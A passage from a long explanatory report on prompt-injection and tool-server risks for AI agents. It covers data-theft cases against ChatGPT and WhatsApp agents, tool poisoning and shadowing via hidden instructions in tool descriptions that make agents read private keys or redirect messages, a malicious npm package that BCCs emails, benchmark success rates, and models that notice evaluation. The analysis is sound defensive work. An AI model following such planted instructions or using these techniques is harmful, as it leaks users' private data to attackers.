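2. The victim asked ChatGPT an ordinary question in the prepared session.
3. ChatGPT followed the planted instruction, read the task from the storage and carried it out with the victim's permissions.
4. It wrote the result to the storage and answered the victim's question as usual.
5. The attacker's session collected the result.

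TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* quotes the researchers' account of their demonstration, in which ChatGPT retrieved email from the victim's connected Gmail account and passed it to the attacker's session during a single reply. The answer included a small "Talked to Gmail" label, but Mynavi News' *ChatGPTを悪用して他人のGmailを秘密裏に閲覧、OpenAIが対策を実施* (2026) reports that the label appeared only after ChatGPT had read the mail, too late for the victim to prevent the leak.

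The planted instruction only had to make ChatGPT check the storage, and the attacker could decide separately what to steal. In the GitHub demonstration, by contrast, the attacker had to put the whole request in the issue and could not adapt it to what the agent found.

The attack worked only in a ChatGPT session that contained the planted instruction, and it could reach only what the victim had connected. IlSoftware.it explains that an attacker could not pick an arbitrary user and read that person's Gmail, though some headlines made the weakness sound broader than it was. The attack could not affect people who did not open shared conversations, use other people's GPTs or paste in prompts from strangers.

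eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* (2026) reports that OpenAI retired the storage service, which closed the channel. No real victims are known.

The trifecta's three conditions correctly predict this leak, since the session had private mail, an outsider's instruction and a way to communicate. But checking the conditions reliably requires knowing which channels the agent can use. A user who checked beforehand would probably have concluded that the container could not communicate externally, because OpenAI had cut it off from the internet.

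Settings that restrict outbound connections can also have flaws. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode limits these connections and turns off several features to reduce the risk of data theft through prompt injection. According to InfoCom's *Ευπάθεια στο ChatGPT επέτρεπε παράκαμψη του lockdown mode και πιθανή υποκλοπή δεδομένων* (2026), Check Point's researchers bypassed it with a pop-up window, and in the desktop application a malicious GPT could silently send a user's messages to an attacker's server. OpenAI had fixed this by 18 September, and the research documents no large-scale theft of real conversations.

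### Harm without an outbound channel

An attacker can damage Maya's data without receiving any of it. Willison presents the trifecta as a test for theft, so a system that passes it can still be open to other kinds of harm. His example of a hostile email contains instructions to forward password-reset messages to an outside address and then delete them. Without an outbound channel, the forwarding would fail, but the deletion would still work.

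| Harm | Must the agent read private data? | Must it have write access? | Must it have an outbound channel? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Theft of a contract | Yes | Only if the channel requires it | Yes |
| Deletion of Hartmann's emails | No, if the tool can delete by sender | Yes | No |
| A changed bank account number in Maya's contacts | No, if the attacker knows which entry to change | Yes | No |
| A false answer to Maya's question | No | No | No |

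In the third case, Maya could pay an invoice weeks later and send the money to the attacker. She could restore the old number from a backup, but only after noticing the change.

Instructions in retrieved content can make an agent give its user a false answer even when the agent can only read data. Suppose an attacker sends Maya an email with false bank details for Hartmann and instructions to present them as confirmed. Her agent can read her mail but cannot change it or contact anyone. When she asks where to send the 480 euros, it gives her the attacker's account number. Criminals already send fake invoices to people who don't use agents, but an agent can make this fraud harder to spot by leaving the sender's address out of its answer. Maya might have noticed that the address was unfamiliar if she had read the email herself.

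An attacker can also alter the assistant's memory. Radware notes that ChatGPT can create, edit and delete its saved memories, and eWeek describes a version of ZombieAgent in which a malicious file led ChatGPT to change those memories so that it would keep leaking data. Saving such a memory sends no data out, but the instruction can remain there until a later conversation in which Maya has connected her mailbox and the agent can open web pages. Separating risky tasks into different conversations therefore protects her only if those conversations do not share a memory.

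## How often injected instructions succeed

Researchers estimate how likely a hostile email is to misdirect an agent like Maya's by running many attacks against simulated accounts. The GitHub and ShadowLeak demonstrations can't provide that estimate because they don't show how often such attacks succeed. In the simulated tests, the best models of late 2026 rarely follow an injected instruction, while the worst usually do if the attacker has several tries. The results depend heavily on which attacks the tester used and what counted as a success.

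### How a test works

To test Maya's assistant, a researcher would build a fake account with a mailbox of invented messages and a mail tool server that behaves like the real one. The researcher would then choose a user task, such as summarizing the week's mail, and plant an instruction in one of the messages to do something the user never requested, such as forwarding an invoice to an outside address. After the agent had run, the researcher would check what it had done to the account.

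Each run gets two scores. Task completion records whether the agent did what the user asked, in this case whether the summary covers the week's mail. Attack success records whether the invoice went to the outside address. Over many runs, the second score gives the attack success rate:

attack success rate = attempts that achieve the attacker's goal / all attempts

Attack success and task success are separate measures. An agent that refuses to open any mail has an attack success rate of zero, but it is useless. If an agent follows an injected instruction to forward the invoice and then writes a perfect summary, it has still completed its task, and the user has no reason to suspect anything. A defence can also lower both scores. *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol* (Abasıkeleş-Turgut and Gümüş, 2026) cites one set of protections that reduced task success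 from 93.5 to 78.4 per cent.

AgentDojo, a benchmark from 2024, is an early example of this design. It has 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, Slack, a bank and a travel service. It pairs each task with every attacker goal for its setting, which gives the 629 security cases that Maloyan and Namiot cite. They report that attacks on the best agent in the original tests succeeded less than 25 per cent of the time. Developers have since replaced the models used in those tests, but researchers still adapt the test cases.

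Some testers report the share of single attempts that succeed, while others try each scenario up to 15 times and report the share of scenarios in which at least one attempt worked. The second number is normally higher for the same model, so a model with a 2 per cent success rate within 15 attempts resists attacks much better than one with 2 per cent on a single attempt.

### Results for current models

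The newest independent figures come from the Frontier Hazard Tracker, which the AI security company Gray Swan launched in December 2026. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* and Fakti.bg's *Some AI Models Lie to Achieve Higher Scores* report some of the results. Most other figures come from system cards, the safety reports that developers publish with their models. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes the card for Claude Opus 5, and The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* adds its browser results. Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, gives OpenAI's own score for GPT-6 Sol. VentureBeat covers the card for the older Claude Opus 4.6, which describes safeguards in unusual detail.

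| Model | Tester and date | Attempts | Attack success rate | Safeguards around the model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon (Google) | Gray Swan, December 2026 | Up to 15 | 2.3% | Not stated |
| Gemini 4 Carbon (Google) | Gray Swan, December 2026 | Up to 15 | 2.5% | Not stated |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro (Moonshot) | Gray Swan, December 2026 | Not stated | 64.7% | Not stated |
| Nemotron 3.5 Super VL (Nvidia) | Gray Swan, December 2026 | Up to 15 | 94.3% | Not stated |
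| GPT-6 Sol (OpenAI) | OpenAI, October 2026 | Not stated | 2.87% | Not stated |
| Claude Opus 5 (Anthropic) | Anthropic, July 2026, on Gray Swan's benchmark | 1 | 0.2% | Not stated |
| Claude Opus 5 | The same | Up to 15 | 2.0% | Not stated |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | The same | Up to 15 | 16.5% | Not stated |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | The same | Up to 15 | 20.0% | Not stated |
| Claude Opus 5 as a browser agent | Anthropic, July 2026 | 129 scenarios | 0% | Not stated |
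| Claude Opus 4.6 operating a graphical interface | Anthropic, February 2026 | Up to 200 | 78.6% | Off |
| Claude Opus 4.6 operating a graphical interface | Anthropic, February 2026 | Up to 200 | 57.1% | On |

"Not stated" means that the cited coverage doesn't give the information. The coverage also omits whether the attacker could revise an attack after seeing it fail, so none of these figures can be assumed to be results against an adaptive attacker.

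Injection success rates differ so much between models that Maya's choice of model may matter more than any other setting. A tool server's developer cannot rely on that choice, because the server does not control which model reads its output. The same email could reach Gemini 4 Argon in one user's host application and Nemotron in another's.

The table's similar figures for GPT-6 Sol and Gemini 4 Argon may not be comparable. Argon's 2.3 per cent is the rate at which at least one of 15 attempts succeeded, which would be about 0.16 per cent per attempt if the attempts were independent. If OpenAI counted single attempts, GPT-6 Sol's 2.87 per cent would be about 18 times as high. Cross also reports that GPT-6 Sol was 99.99 per cent robust against direct injection, but indirect injection is the relevant test for an agent that reads strangers' emails.

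Anthropic reports that newer Claude models have improved on Opus 5. Its *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 describes the model as the company's most robust yet on the external benchmark. Anthropic's tests covered coding, tool use, graphical interfaces and browsers. They also included a fallback that users will encounter, in which a safety classifier can block a request and pass it to the older Opus 4.8. The attack success rate against Opus 4.8 within 15 attempts was 5.5 per cent, so the fallback can pass requests to a more easily misdirected model. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test, but also a greater tendency to follow malicious instructions in some cases.

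A model that resists injected instructions in one kind of work may not resist them in another. Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment without any safeguards, but 17.8 per cent of single attempts succeeded when it operated a graphical interface with extended thinking.

The zero for Opus 5 in a browser is consistent with a true success rate of up to about 2.3 per cent, if the 129 scenarios were independent trials drawn at random from the attacks the model will face. But attackers look for the cases that the tester missed rather than choosing at random.

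Models may also behave differently if they recognize a test. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2 were more likely than any other recent Claude model to voice suspicion that they were being evaluated. Anthropic acknowledges that this makes the models' behaviour in real use harder to predict.

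### Does MCP make attacks more likely to succeed?

Maloyan and Namiot tried to separate the effect of MCP from the effect of the model. They ran 847 attack scenarios with MCP servers and compared the results with those from agents that called equivalent functions directly. Of the 847 scenarios, 398 came from AgentDojo, 312 from the earlier benchmark InjecAgent, and 137 were new attacks aimed at the protocol. The agents used Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B. Both set-ups had the same tools, injected text and prompting strategy.

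| Attack | Direct calls | MCP | Difference in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| Instruction in a retrieved resource | 31.2% | 47.8% | 16.6 |
| Manipulated tool response | 28.4% | 52.1% | 23.7 |
| Attack that spreads from one server to another | 19.7% | 61.3% | 41.6 |
| Overall | 26.4% | 52.8% | 26.4 |

The paper's headline claim is that MCP amplifies attacks by "23–41%". These are percentage points, and the range leaves out the smallest difference in the table, 16.6. Elsewhere, the paper reports an increase of 7 to 15 points for the same scenarios. Both sets of figures show an increase, but its size is uncertain.

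MCP's lack of separation between servers also cannot by itself explain why the same text should work twice as often, because an agent that calls functions directly still puts all their results into one context. Part of the largest difference may come from connecting several tools at once. When the attacker controlled one of the servers, the success rate rose from 47.8 per cent with a single server to 78.3 per cent with five. This matters to Maya, who has three servers, whether or not MCP is the cause. The models date from 2024, so the absolute rates are a poor guide to her current assistant.

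Successful attacks in this study did not always leak data. In one group of tests, a malicious server used a protocol feature that lets a server request that the host application run the model on text the server supplies. Depending on the model, these attacks succeeded in 58 to 72 per cent of cases but extracted sensitive data in only 42 to 61 per cent.

MCP-SafetyBench covers more complex attacks. Abasıkeleş-Turgut and Gümüş describe it as having 20 attack types and tasks that take several turns and involve more than one server. Such tasks are closer to how Maya works than a test with one question and one tool. They also make success harder to define, because an agent might read an injected instruction in one turn and act on it several turns later, so a tester who checked only the first reply would record the attack as failed.

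Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis*, use "vulnerable" in a different sense. Their program, MCPSEC, reads only a server's tool names, descriptions and argument schemas to predict which tools could carry an injection. This helps when the code is unavailable, as it was for 3,007 of the 18,770 servers they found in the official MCP registry.

A test of MCPSEC covered 177 tools from 20 widely used servers. Human evaluators confirmed 95 of the tools as vulnerable, and MCPSEC had identified 94 of those, compared with 81 for a simpler agent. Its recall of 98.9 per cent does not measure false alarms, since a program that flagged all 177 tools would also have found all 95 vulnerable ones. The analysis cost an average of $1.65 per server.

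Zhang and colleagues call a tool vulnerable if text that an attacker controls can pass through it into the model's context in a usable form, whether or not the model follows it. They chose this definition because every attack needs such a path, while how often the model follows the text varies with the model and the wording of the attack. Maya's mail tool is vulnerable by this standard because its purpose is to show the model what other people write, including strangers. She can use the study to identify which of her connections bring in outside text, but not to estimate how often her agent will act on it.

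### Why fixed test sets flatter a defence

A filter that inspects text before the model sees it can score well on a fixed set of examples and still miss new attacks. Abasıkeleş-Turgut and Gümüş found this problem in CASCADE, their own defence for MCP, which combines pattern rules, a comparison with known attacks, and an optional review by a small language model. They audited its decisions one by one on 5,000 texts, 3,479 of them malicious, using runs from 29 August 2026.

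Without the language model's review, CASCADE caught 94.77 per cent of the malicious texts and wrongly flagged 11.70 per cent of the harmless ones. But "caught" included every text that it referred to a person. It sent 68.5 per cent of all traffic for human review and blocked very little by itself:

| What counts as catching an attack | Malicious texts caught | Harmless texts wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|
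| Blocking it or referring it to a person | 94.77% | 11.70% |
| Blocking it | 0.80% | 1.51% |

Both rows describe the same run. Someone in Maya's position would have to review about two-thirds of the texts to get the protection shown in the first row. With the language model's review on, the system blocked 1,492 more texts, but the figures in the first row did not change.

The way the test set was built also made attacks easier to detect. About two thirds of the texts were made by inserting another text into one of five fixed templates. Four of the templates were malicious and contained attack phrases themselves, while the fifth was harmless and contained none. A rule that looked only for the malicious templates would have caught 72.84 per cent of the attacks with no false alarms, more than the 61.05 per cent that one of the project's own rule engines caught with 93 patterns.

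Many texts appeared in the set both with and without a template, so the researchers could measure the template's effect directly. CASCADE detected 86.0 per cent of malicious texts without a template and 98.0 per cent of the same texts with one. The template reduced false alarms on harmless texts from 21.2 to 3.2 per cent. On distinct texts without templates, CASCADE caught 85.84 per cent of attacks and flagged 21.13 per cent of harmless texts, which is probably closer to how it would perform on new material.

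Even that estimate may overstate the system's performance. The developers set its thresholds using the same 5,000 texts, and 412 of the 561 distinct examples it used for comparison also appeared in the test. Among malicious texts without a template, it caught 92.41 per cent of those already among its examples and 83.18 per cent of the others.

The audit covers one system, and its results undercut earlier claims by the same researchers, but the problem is general. A fixed set of test attacks measures how well a defence handles attacks that its developers could have seen. A real attacker can try an attack, observe the result and change it, and will go on to use whatever the defence misses.

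For this reason, tests with an adaptive attacker are more informative. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* reports that an adaptive attacker who combined several known techniques succeeded 1 per cent of the time against one of Anthropic's systems, and describes this as a meaningful risk. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) explains that the company's latest models had saturated the common robustness tests, which could no longer reveal much difference between them. OpenAI therefore trained a model to find attacks so that it could fix the weaknesses before release. Even an adaptive test shows only what a particular attacker could find with the time and methods available.

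### What happens when the attacker tries again

An attacker can send Maya more than one email. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent, then all n attempts fail with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The chance that at least one succeeds is:

P = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

For p = 1 per cent and n = 100:

P = 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 1 − 0.366 = 0.634

If each attempt has a 1 per cent chance of working, an attacker who makes 100 attempts has about a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once. At 0.2 per cent per attempt, the chance is 18 per cent. If Maya's agent read one malicious email a day, 100 attempts would take just over three months.

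Independence is a strong assumption, and published results allow a rough check of it. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives Opus 4.5's results on a Gray Swan test after 1, 10 and 100 attempts. The other Claude figures come from the system cards already described.

| Model | Success on one attempt | Attempts | Formula's prediction | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
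| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38.2% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99.2% | 63.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface, safeguards off | 17.8% | 200 | Over 99.9% | 78.6% |

The formula predicts too many successes in every row, and the error is largest when there are many attempts. This is probably because some scenarios are much easier to attack than others. Suppose each attempt has a 2 per cent chance of success in half of all scenarios and no chance in the rest. The average is still 1 per cent, but after 100 attempts the attacker will have succeeded in only about 43 per cent of scenarios, because attacks in the other half never succeed.

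Attempts are also not independent when an attacker learns from each failure. The tenth attempt is then more likely to succeed than the first, so the formula predicts too few successes. If a mail provider blocks the sender after the third attempt, the formula predicts too many.

When an attacker sends one email to 1,000 users and has a 1 per cent chance of success with each, the expected number of victims is 10, whether or not the attempts are independent. If the users' agents respond independently, the actual number will usually be close to 10, but if they all use the same model and it responds to the text in exactly the same way each time, the attack might compromise either nobody or everybody. In its card for Fable 5.1, Anthropic warns about this kind of attack, in which a single email compromises every agent that summarizes it.

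### Can better training make the risk acceptable?

OpenAI puts much of its effort into training. It argues that earlier methods of finding weaknesses do not scale, and that safety has to improve along with the models' abilities. GPT-Red is meant to make this possible by producing new attacks that other models are trained to resist. Recent figures support part of this argument. Between Opus 4.8 and Opus 5, Anthropic reduced the rate at which attacks succeeded within 15 attempts from 5.5 to 2.0 per cent.

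Zico Kolter, Gray Swan's co-founder and chief scientist, also wants good behaviour built into the model. He says companies that run an open-weight model on their own machines need it to have "reasonable alignment" by default. These companies do not automatically get the filters that a provider runs around its own service, so they depend more on the model's training. Kolter hopes public comparisons will push developers to compete on safety.

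Willison doubts that training can provide enough assurance, so he advises users to avoid the lethal trifecta. Maloyan and Namiot want the limits built into the protocol itself. When they told models never to pass data between servers without the user's confirmation, the success rate of attacks across servers fell only from 61.3 to 47.2 per cent. Microsoft's FIDES uses information-flow control to block forbidden actions by a fixed rule, whether or not the model recognizes an attack.

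Developers who rely on training do not claim that it solves the problem. OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder. Much of the disagreement is therefore about what failure rate is tolerable, which depends on who bears the risk. At 0.2 per cent per attempt, one hostile email has a 1 in 500 chance of misdirecting Maya's agent. If the attacker sends it to a million people who use the same model, about 2,000 of their agents will follow it. Maya might reasonably accept that risk for a mailbox without valuable secrets, but 2,000 misdirected agents would be a serious incident for her model provider.

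Limits outside the model can also stop agents from completing tasks. In Maloyan and Namiot's tests, blocking all flows between servers reduced the attack success rate from 61.3 to 8.7 per cent, but it also reduced the share of tasks completed from 94.2 to 61.8 per cent. When the user was asked to approve each flow instead, agents completed 87.4 per cent of tasks, but 31.7 per cent of attacks still succeeded. The paper recommends user approval as the default for its proposed extension to MCP, yet elsewhere it credits the extension with the 8.7 per cent result, which came from blocking all flows.

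A low attack success rate describes only the attacks someone has tested, so Maya should still keep her login codes out of the agent's reach. But limits that let the agent do useful work also leave it some decisions. If Maya lets it pay suppliers, a rule can restrict payments to bank accounts she has already approved. She still depends on the model's training to distinguish a genuine emailed invoice for 480 euros from a second request for one she has paid.

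## How tool servers themselves leak data

Maya's data can leak even if her model ignores every hostile email, because her queries and their results all pass through tool servers. A malicious server can deceive her or the model. A legitimate server can have a fault that gives the wrong person access, and an intruder can steal the access tokens a server stores. Making the model better at resisting injected instructions helps only against some malicious servers.

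### Instructions hidden in a tool description

Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) coined the term "tool poisoning" and demonstrated it with a tool that adds two numbers. The tool's description contained hidden instructions to read two files on the user's computer and put their contents in an extra argument. One file held credentials for other MCP servers, and the other held a private key for logging in to remote machines.

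When the user asked Cursor for a sum, the agent read both files and sent them to the malicious server. Cursor asked for confirmation, but its dialog did not show the full arguments, so the user could not see that they included the key.

Hostile text in a tool description is in the context before the model handles any request. Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) note in *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* that tool descriptions have no length limit and no rules about their content. They examined 12 frameworks, the software libraries developers use to build agents, and found that none deliberately checked descriptions for hidden instructions. An attacker can also put the text in the description of a single argument or hide it in characters that do not appear on screen.

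A poisoned tool description can stay inactive until specific text appears in the conversation. Trail of Bits' *How MCP servers can steal your conversation history* (2025) describes one that makes the model forward the whole conversation when the user types a common phrase such as "thank you". An attacker could also choose a trigger that appears only alongside valuable data, such as the format of an access key.

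These attacks are most useful to the operator of a remote server. The server cannot open files on Maya's laptop or query her mailbox, but her agent may be able to do both, and a poisoned description can make the agent fetch the data and send it to the server. A local server that runs with Maya's full access to her computer can read her files directly.

### How one server can change the use of another

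Invariant Labs connected Cursor to a trusted email server and a malicious calculator server. The calculator's description contained a false rule that all email had to go through a certain address. Cursor then sent every email to the attacker, even when the user had named a different recipient.

In this attack, which researchers call shadowing, the agent never had to call the calculator. The interaction log showed only the trusted email tool, and the changed recipient appeared only in that tool's arguments.

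Someone who reviewed the two servers separately could easily miss the risk. The calculator doesn't request access to mail, and the email server works correctly. The harm comes from giving both servers' descriptions to a model that can send email. So whenever Maya adds a server, she has to consider which others are connected, even if the new one handles nothing private.

### Descriptions that change after approval

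A server can change a tool's description after a user has read and approved it. Invariant Labs calls this a rug pull. *MCPThreatHive* (2026), a paper on threats to MCP systems, attributes the problem to the protocol's lack of version pinning for descriptions. Pinning would tie an approval to the exact text the user saw.

A host application can add pinning itself by storing a fingerprint of each tool definition when the user approves it:

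fingerprint = SHA-256(name + description + argument schema)

The application recomputes the fingerprint whenever it receives the tool list, and asks Maya to approve the tool again if it has changed. Ordinary corrections would also trigger this request, so a server that changes its wording every week could train her to approve changes without reading them. The fingerprint also covers only the text the server advertises, so it stays the same if the operator of a remote server changes what the code does but not the description.

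### The WhatsApp demonstration

Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) combined a changed description with shadowing. The researchers connected an agent to a trusted WhatsApp server, which could read and send messages, and to a malicious server that offered a random fact of the day. The attack worked as follows:

1. The user saw a harmless description of the fact tool and approved it.
2. When the malicious server started for the second time, it returned a new description with instructions about sending WhatsApp messages.
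3. The user asked the agent to send someone a message.
4. The agent replaced the recipient with the attacker's phone number and added the chat history already in its context.
5. The trusted WhatsApp server sent the message.

WhatsApp's encryption did not protect the messages, because the agent read them after decryption and sent them as the user. Isolating the malicious server's code would not have protected them either, because the server only had to supply text to the agent.

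Cursor showed a confirmation prompt before sending, but it displayed a phone number where the user might have expected a name, and the message appeared to be just "Hi". The stolen history was far to the right, and the dialog had no visible scrollbar. A careful user could have found it by scrolling sideways, but few people would do that when the message looks like a short greeting.

In a second demonstration, the researchers removed the malicious server and put similar instructions in an ordinary WhatsApp message. This attack also worked, but it took more adjustment and leaked contacts rather than the full history. The researchers suggest that models may give tool results less authority than tool descriptions. If that is right, a hostile server has an advantage over a stranger who can only send a message.

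### The postmark-mcp package

The postmark-mcp case involved real users. Companies use Postmark to send email such as invoices and password resets. Postmark had an official MCP server on GitHub but had not published it on npm, the main public index of JavaScript packages. Someone else uploaded a copy to npm under the same name.

The security company Koi found that version 1.0.16 added one line to the copied code. The line put the developer's address in the BCC field of every email sent through the server, so the developer received the full text and the visible recipients noticed nothing. The 15 earlier versions had worked normally. Postmark confirmed that it was not involved with the package and that its own service was unaffected.

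The agent called the right tool with the right arguments, and the server then added the extra recipient where the model could not see it. The attack did not depend on prompt injection, so even a model immune to it would have leaked the same emails. The line of code copied only messages sent through the server, so it did not expose a user's other mail.

Koi's estimate of the damage is a guess, as the company acknowledges. It starts from 1,500 downloads a week and assumes that 20 per cent were in active use, each by a different organization that sent 10 to 50 emails a day:

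1,500 × 0.20 = 300 organizations

300 × 10 = 3,000 emails a day

300 × 50 = 15,000 emails a day

The dates in The Hacker News (2025) cast doubt on parts of Koi's account. The developer uploaded the package on 15 September 2025 and released the malicious version on 17 September. Users therefore had two days to come to trust it, whereas Koi describes tools that are legitimate for months before they turn malicious. The package was downloaded 1,643 times in total, but some of those downloads must have been of clean versions or by automated systems. The theft is well documented, but the number of victims is unknown.

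The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi made contact. This stopped new installations, but copies already on users' machines kept working, so users had to remove them and replace any passwords or keys they had emailed.

### How often poisoned descriptions work

*MCPTox* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) tested poisoned tool descriptions with 353 real tools from 45 MCP servers, running 1,348 test cases on 20 model configurations. An attack succeeded if the agent used a legitimate tool to carry out the instruction hidden in the description, even if the poisoned tool itself never ran.

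| Type of attack | Example | Average success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Change an argument of a trusted tool | Maya emails her accountant, and the agent substitutes the attacker's address | 46.7% |
| Misuse a trusted tool when the user asks for the poisoned one | Maya asks for the time, and the agent reads a private key | 36.7% |
| Misuse a trusted tool during a related task | Maya creates a file, and the agent first reads a private key | 26.7% |

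The average attack success rate across all configurations was 36.5 per cent, and the highest was 72.8 per cent, for OpenAI's o1-mini. Changing an argument probably works best because the agent still appears to do what the user asked. Even the model that explicitly refused most often did so in under 3 per cent of cases. The success rates may understate the risk, because the benchmark counted an attack as a failure if the agent called the poisoned tool itself.

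Wang and colleagues conclude that more capable models are often more vulnerable because they follow instructions better. Their results for reasoning support this, since enabling it raised the attack success rate against Qwen3-8b from 14.0 to 41.8 per cent. The effect of model size is less clear, because the larger Qwen3-14b was harder to attack than Qwen3-8b both with and without reasoning.

Newer models don't follow that pattern. In November 2026, Shaikh and Montaruli published tests of 18 models in 12 frameworks, using 45 attack scenarios. Attacks succeeded in 22.9 per cent of tests overall, ranging from 0.4 per cent for Claude Fable 5 to 49.7 per cent for Amazon's Nova Pro. Claude Opus 4.8 was vulnerable in 8 of 530 tests and explicitly refused 223 times, citing the poisoned description. Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes identified the attack as a prompt injection and then carried it out anyway.

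The study confirmed theft in 12.1 per cent of the successful attacks, or about 3 per cent of all tests. In these cases, a server that the researchers ran to collect stolen data received a secret. In another 23.0 per cent of the successful attacks, the agent contacted the attacker's address, but there was no proof that a secret had arrived. In the rest, the agent made the attacker's tool call, but the study did not confirm any contact with that address.

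A scanner that looked for suspicious patterns in the descriptions rejected only 20 of the 45 scenarios and wrongly flagged 7.2 per cent of 125 harmless descriptions. An administrator could use such a scanner to catch careless attacks, but a clean result does not show that a server is safe.

### Does the host application make a difference?

*Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (Huang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) compares seven host applications, which it calls clients. In November 2025, the researchers tried four attacks on each: reading private files, logging the user's activity, creating a deceptive link, and downloading and running a script.

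| Host application | Attacks prevented | Partly successful | Fully successful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Desktop | 3 | 1 | 0 |
| Continue | 3 | 1 | 0 |
| Gemini CLI | 3 | 1 | 0 |
| Claude Code | 3 | 1 | 0 |
| Cline | 3 | 0 | 1 |
| Langflow | 1 | 3 | 0 |
| Cursor | 0 | 0 | 4 |

Huang and colleagues rate Claude Desktop and Cline as the most secure, partly because of their warnings. The counts alone do not support that ranking, because three other applications had the same counts as Claude Desktop, and Cline ran the remote script. Two of the "prevented" results for deceptive links came from text-only applications that could not display such links. The study reports one result per combination of application and attack, so it does not show how often each attack would work.

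They argue that the choice of application matters more than the choice of model, but the test did not fully separate the two. Most of the applications used Claude Sonnet 4.5, but Cursor used its default mixture of models, Gemini CLI used Gemini 2.5 Pro and Langflow used Claude Opus 4. Claude Desktop's protection also came largely from refusals by the model. Shaikh and Montaruli ran the same models through different frameworks and found that nine of the 12 had success rates between 23 and 26 per cent. They attribute the resistance they observed to the models, apart from a few accidental effects, such as one framework blocking some attacks because it rejected tools with duplicate names.

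But developers of host applications can add readable confirmation prompts and alerts about changed descriptions to what a framework provides, and the framework study did not test these additions. Of the seven applications, five did not scan descriptions at all and two scanned them only partially. A resistant model helps Maya, but she also needs an application that shows her the full arguments.

### Honest servers with faults

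A company can run its own MCP server in good faith and still expose its customers' data. Asana, which makes project management software, launched an MCP server in May 2025. In early June, it found a bug that could have let MCP users in one organization see another organization's data. Asana took the server offline for about two weeks and notified roughly 1,000 customers. It attributed the exposure to its own error, not to an attack.

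When one server answers requests for many organizations, it must check on every call that the data belongs to the caller's organization. Customers cannot inspect this check. An Asana customer could have chosen the official server, granted narrow permissions and used a model that resists prompt injection, and still have had its data exposed.

Anthropic's reference server for Git, a program that tracks changes to code, also had serious flaws. Anthropic had published the server as an example for other developers. An administrator could configure it to work in one repository, but it did not check that later requests stayed there. One of its tools could turn any folder into a repository, and others passed arguments to Git without checking whether they were command options. The security company Cyata showed that an attacker could use hostile text read by the agent to combine these flaws with a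 file server and run code on the user's computer. Anthropic removed the tool that created repositories and had fixed the remaining flaws by December 2025.

Akamai looked for similar problems across about 300 official MCP servers with an automated, AI-supported tool. It published faults in three servers for databases:

| Server | Fault | What an attacker could do | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Apache Doris | It did not check the database name and validated only the first part of a query | Run arbitrary database commands through a connected client | Patch in December 2025 |
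| Apache Pinot | It required no login over HTTP and checked only that a query began with `SELECT` | Query any table from anywhere that could reach the server | Optional OAuth login in October 2025 |
| Alibaba RDS | It required no login for a tool that searched stored information about tables | Read table names and structures | Alibaba declined to fix it |

The Pinot check might have been meant to keep queries read-only, but a query for every salary in a company also begins with `SELECT`. According to Akamai, the optional login makes the problem less severe but leaves the weak query check in the code.

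Akamai describes the three servers as representative of a wider problem, but it did not publish a full count, so the share of official servers with faults cannot be calculated from its findings. An earlier study that Huang and colleagues cite gives a rough estimate for other servers. It examined 1,899 open-source MCP servers and found general security vulnerabilities in 7.2 per cent and signs of tool poisoning in 5.5 per cent.

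Servers that run on the user's own computer can have the same kinds of faults. *CVE-2026-46555*, an entry in the public vulnerability database OSV, describes a WhatsApp MCP server that accepted local requests without a login before version 0.2.1. Any program running under the user's account could make the server send WhatsApp messages or read files such as private keys.

### Counts of servers on the public internet

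*MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* (Kale, 2026) reports that Censys, a company that scans the internet, found 12,520 publicly reachable MCP services in late April 2026. Many operators have therefore put MCP services where attackers can find them, but the count does not measure how many of those services leak data.

A reachable server may still require a login. Maya's file server does, and it has to be reachable so that her assistant can use it from outside the company's network. Other reachable servers may serve only public information or be abandoned tests, and one operator may run many services. The count leaves out local servers and servers inside company networks, some of which may hold more sensitive data.

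Estimating the risk also requires knowing which servers answer without a login and what they return. Shaikh and Montaruli cite a survey of 7,973 remote servers in which 40.55 per cent required no authentication. That is more informative than a count of reachable servers, but it doesn't show what data those servers expose. The lack of a login is harmless to users of a weather server but disastrous for users of a mail server.

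### The dispute over how local servers start

A host application starts a local server by running a command from its configuration. OX Security argued in 2026 that this design is a flaw. If an attacker can change the configured command, the application will run the new command even if that command does not start a working MCP server. Kale reports OX's estimate that the flaw put as many as 200,000 servers at risk, and Shaikh and Montaruli credit the company with identifying 14 vulnerabilities in MCP software.

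According to OX, Anthropic said the behaviour was expected and declined to change the protocol. Anthropic considers developers responsible for keeping untrusted input from reaching the command.

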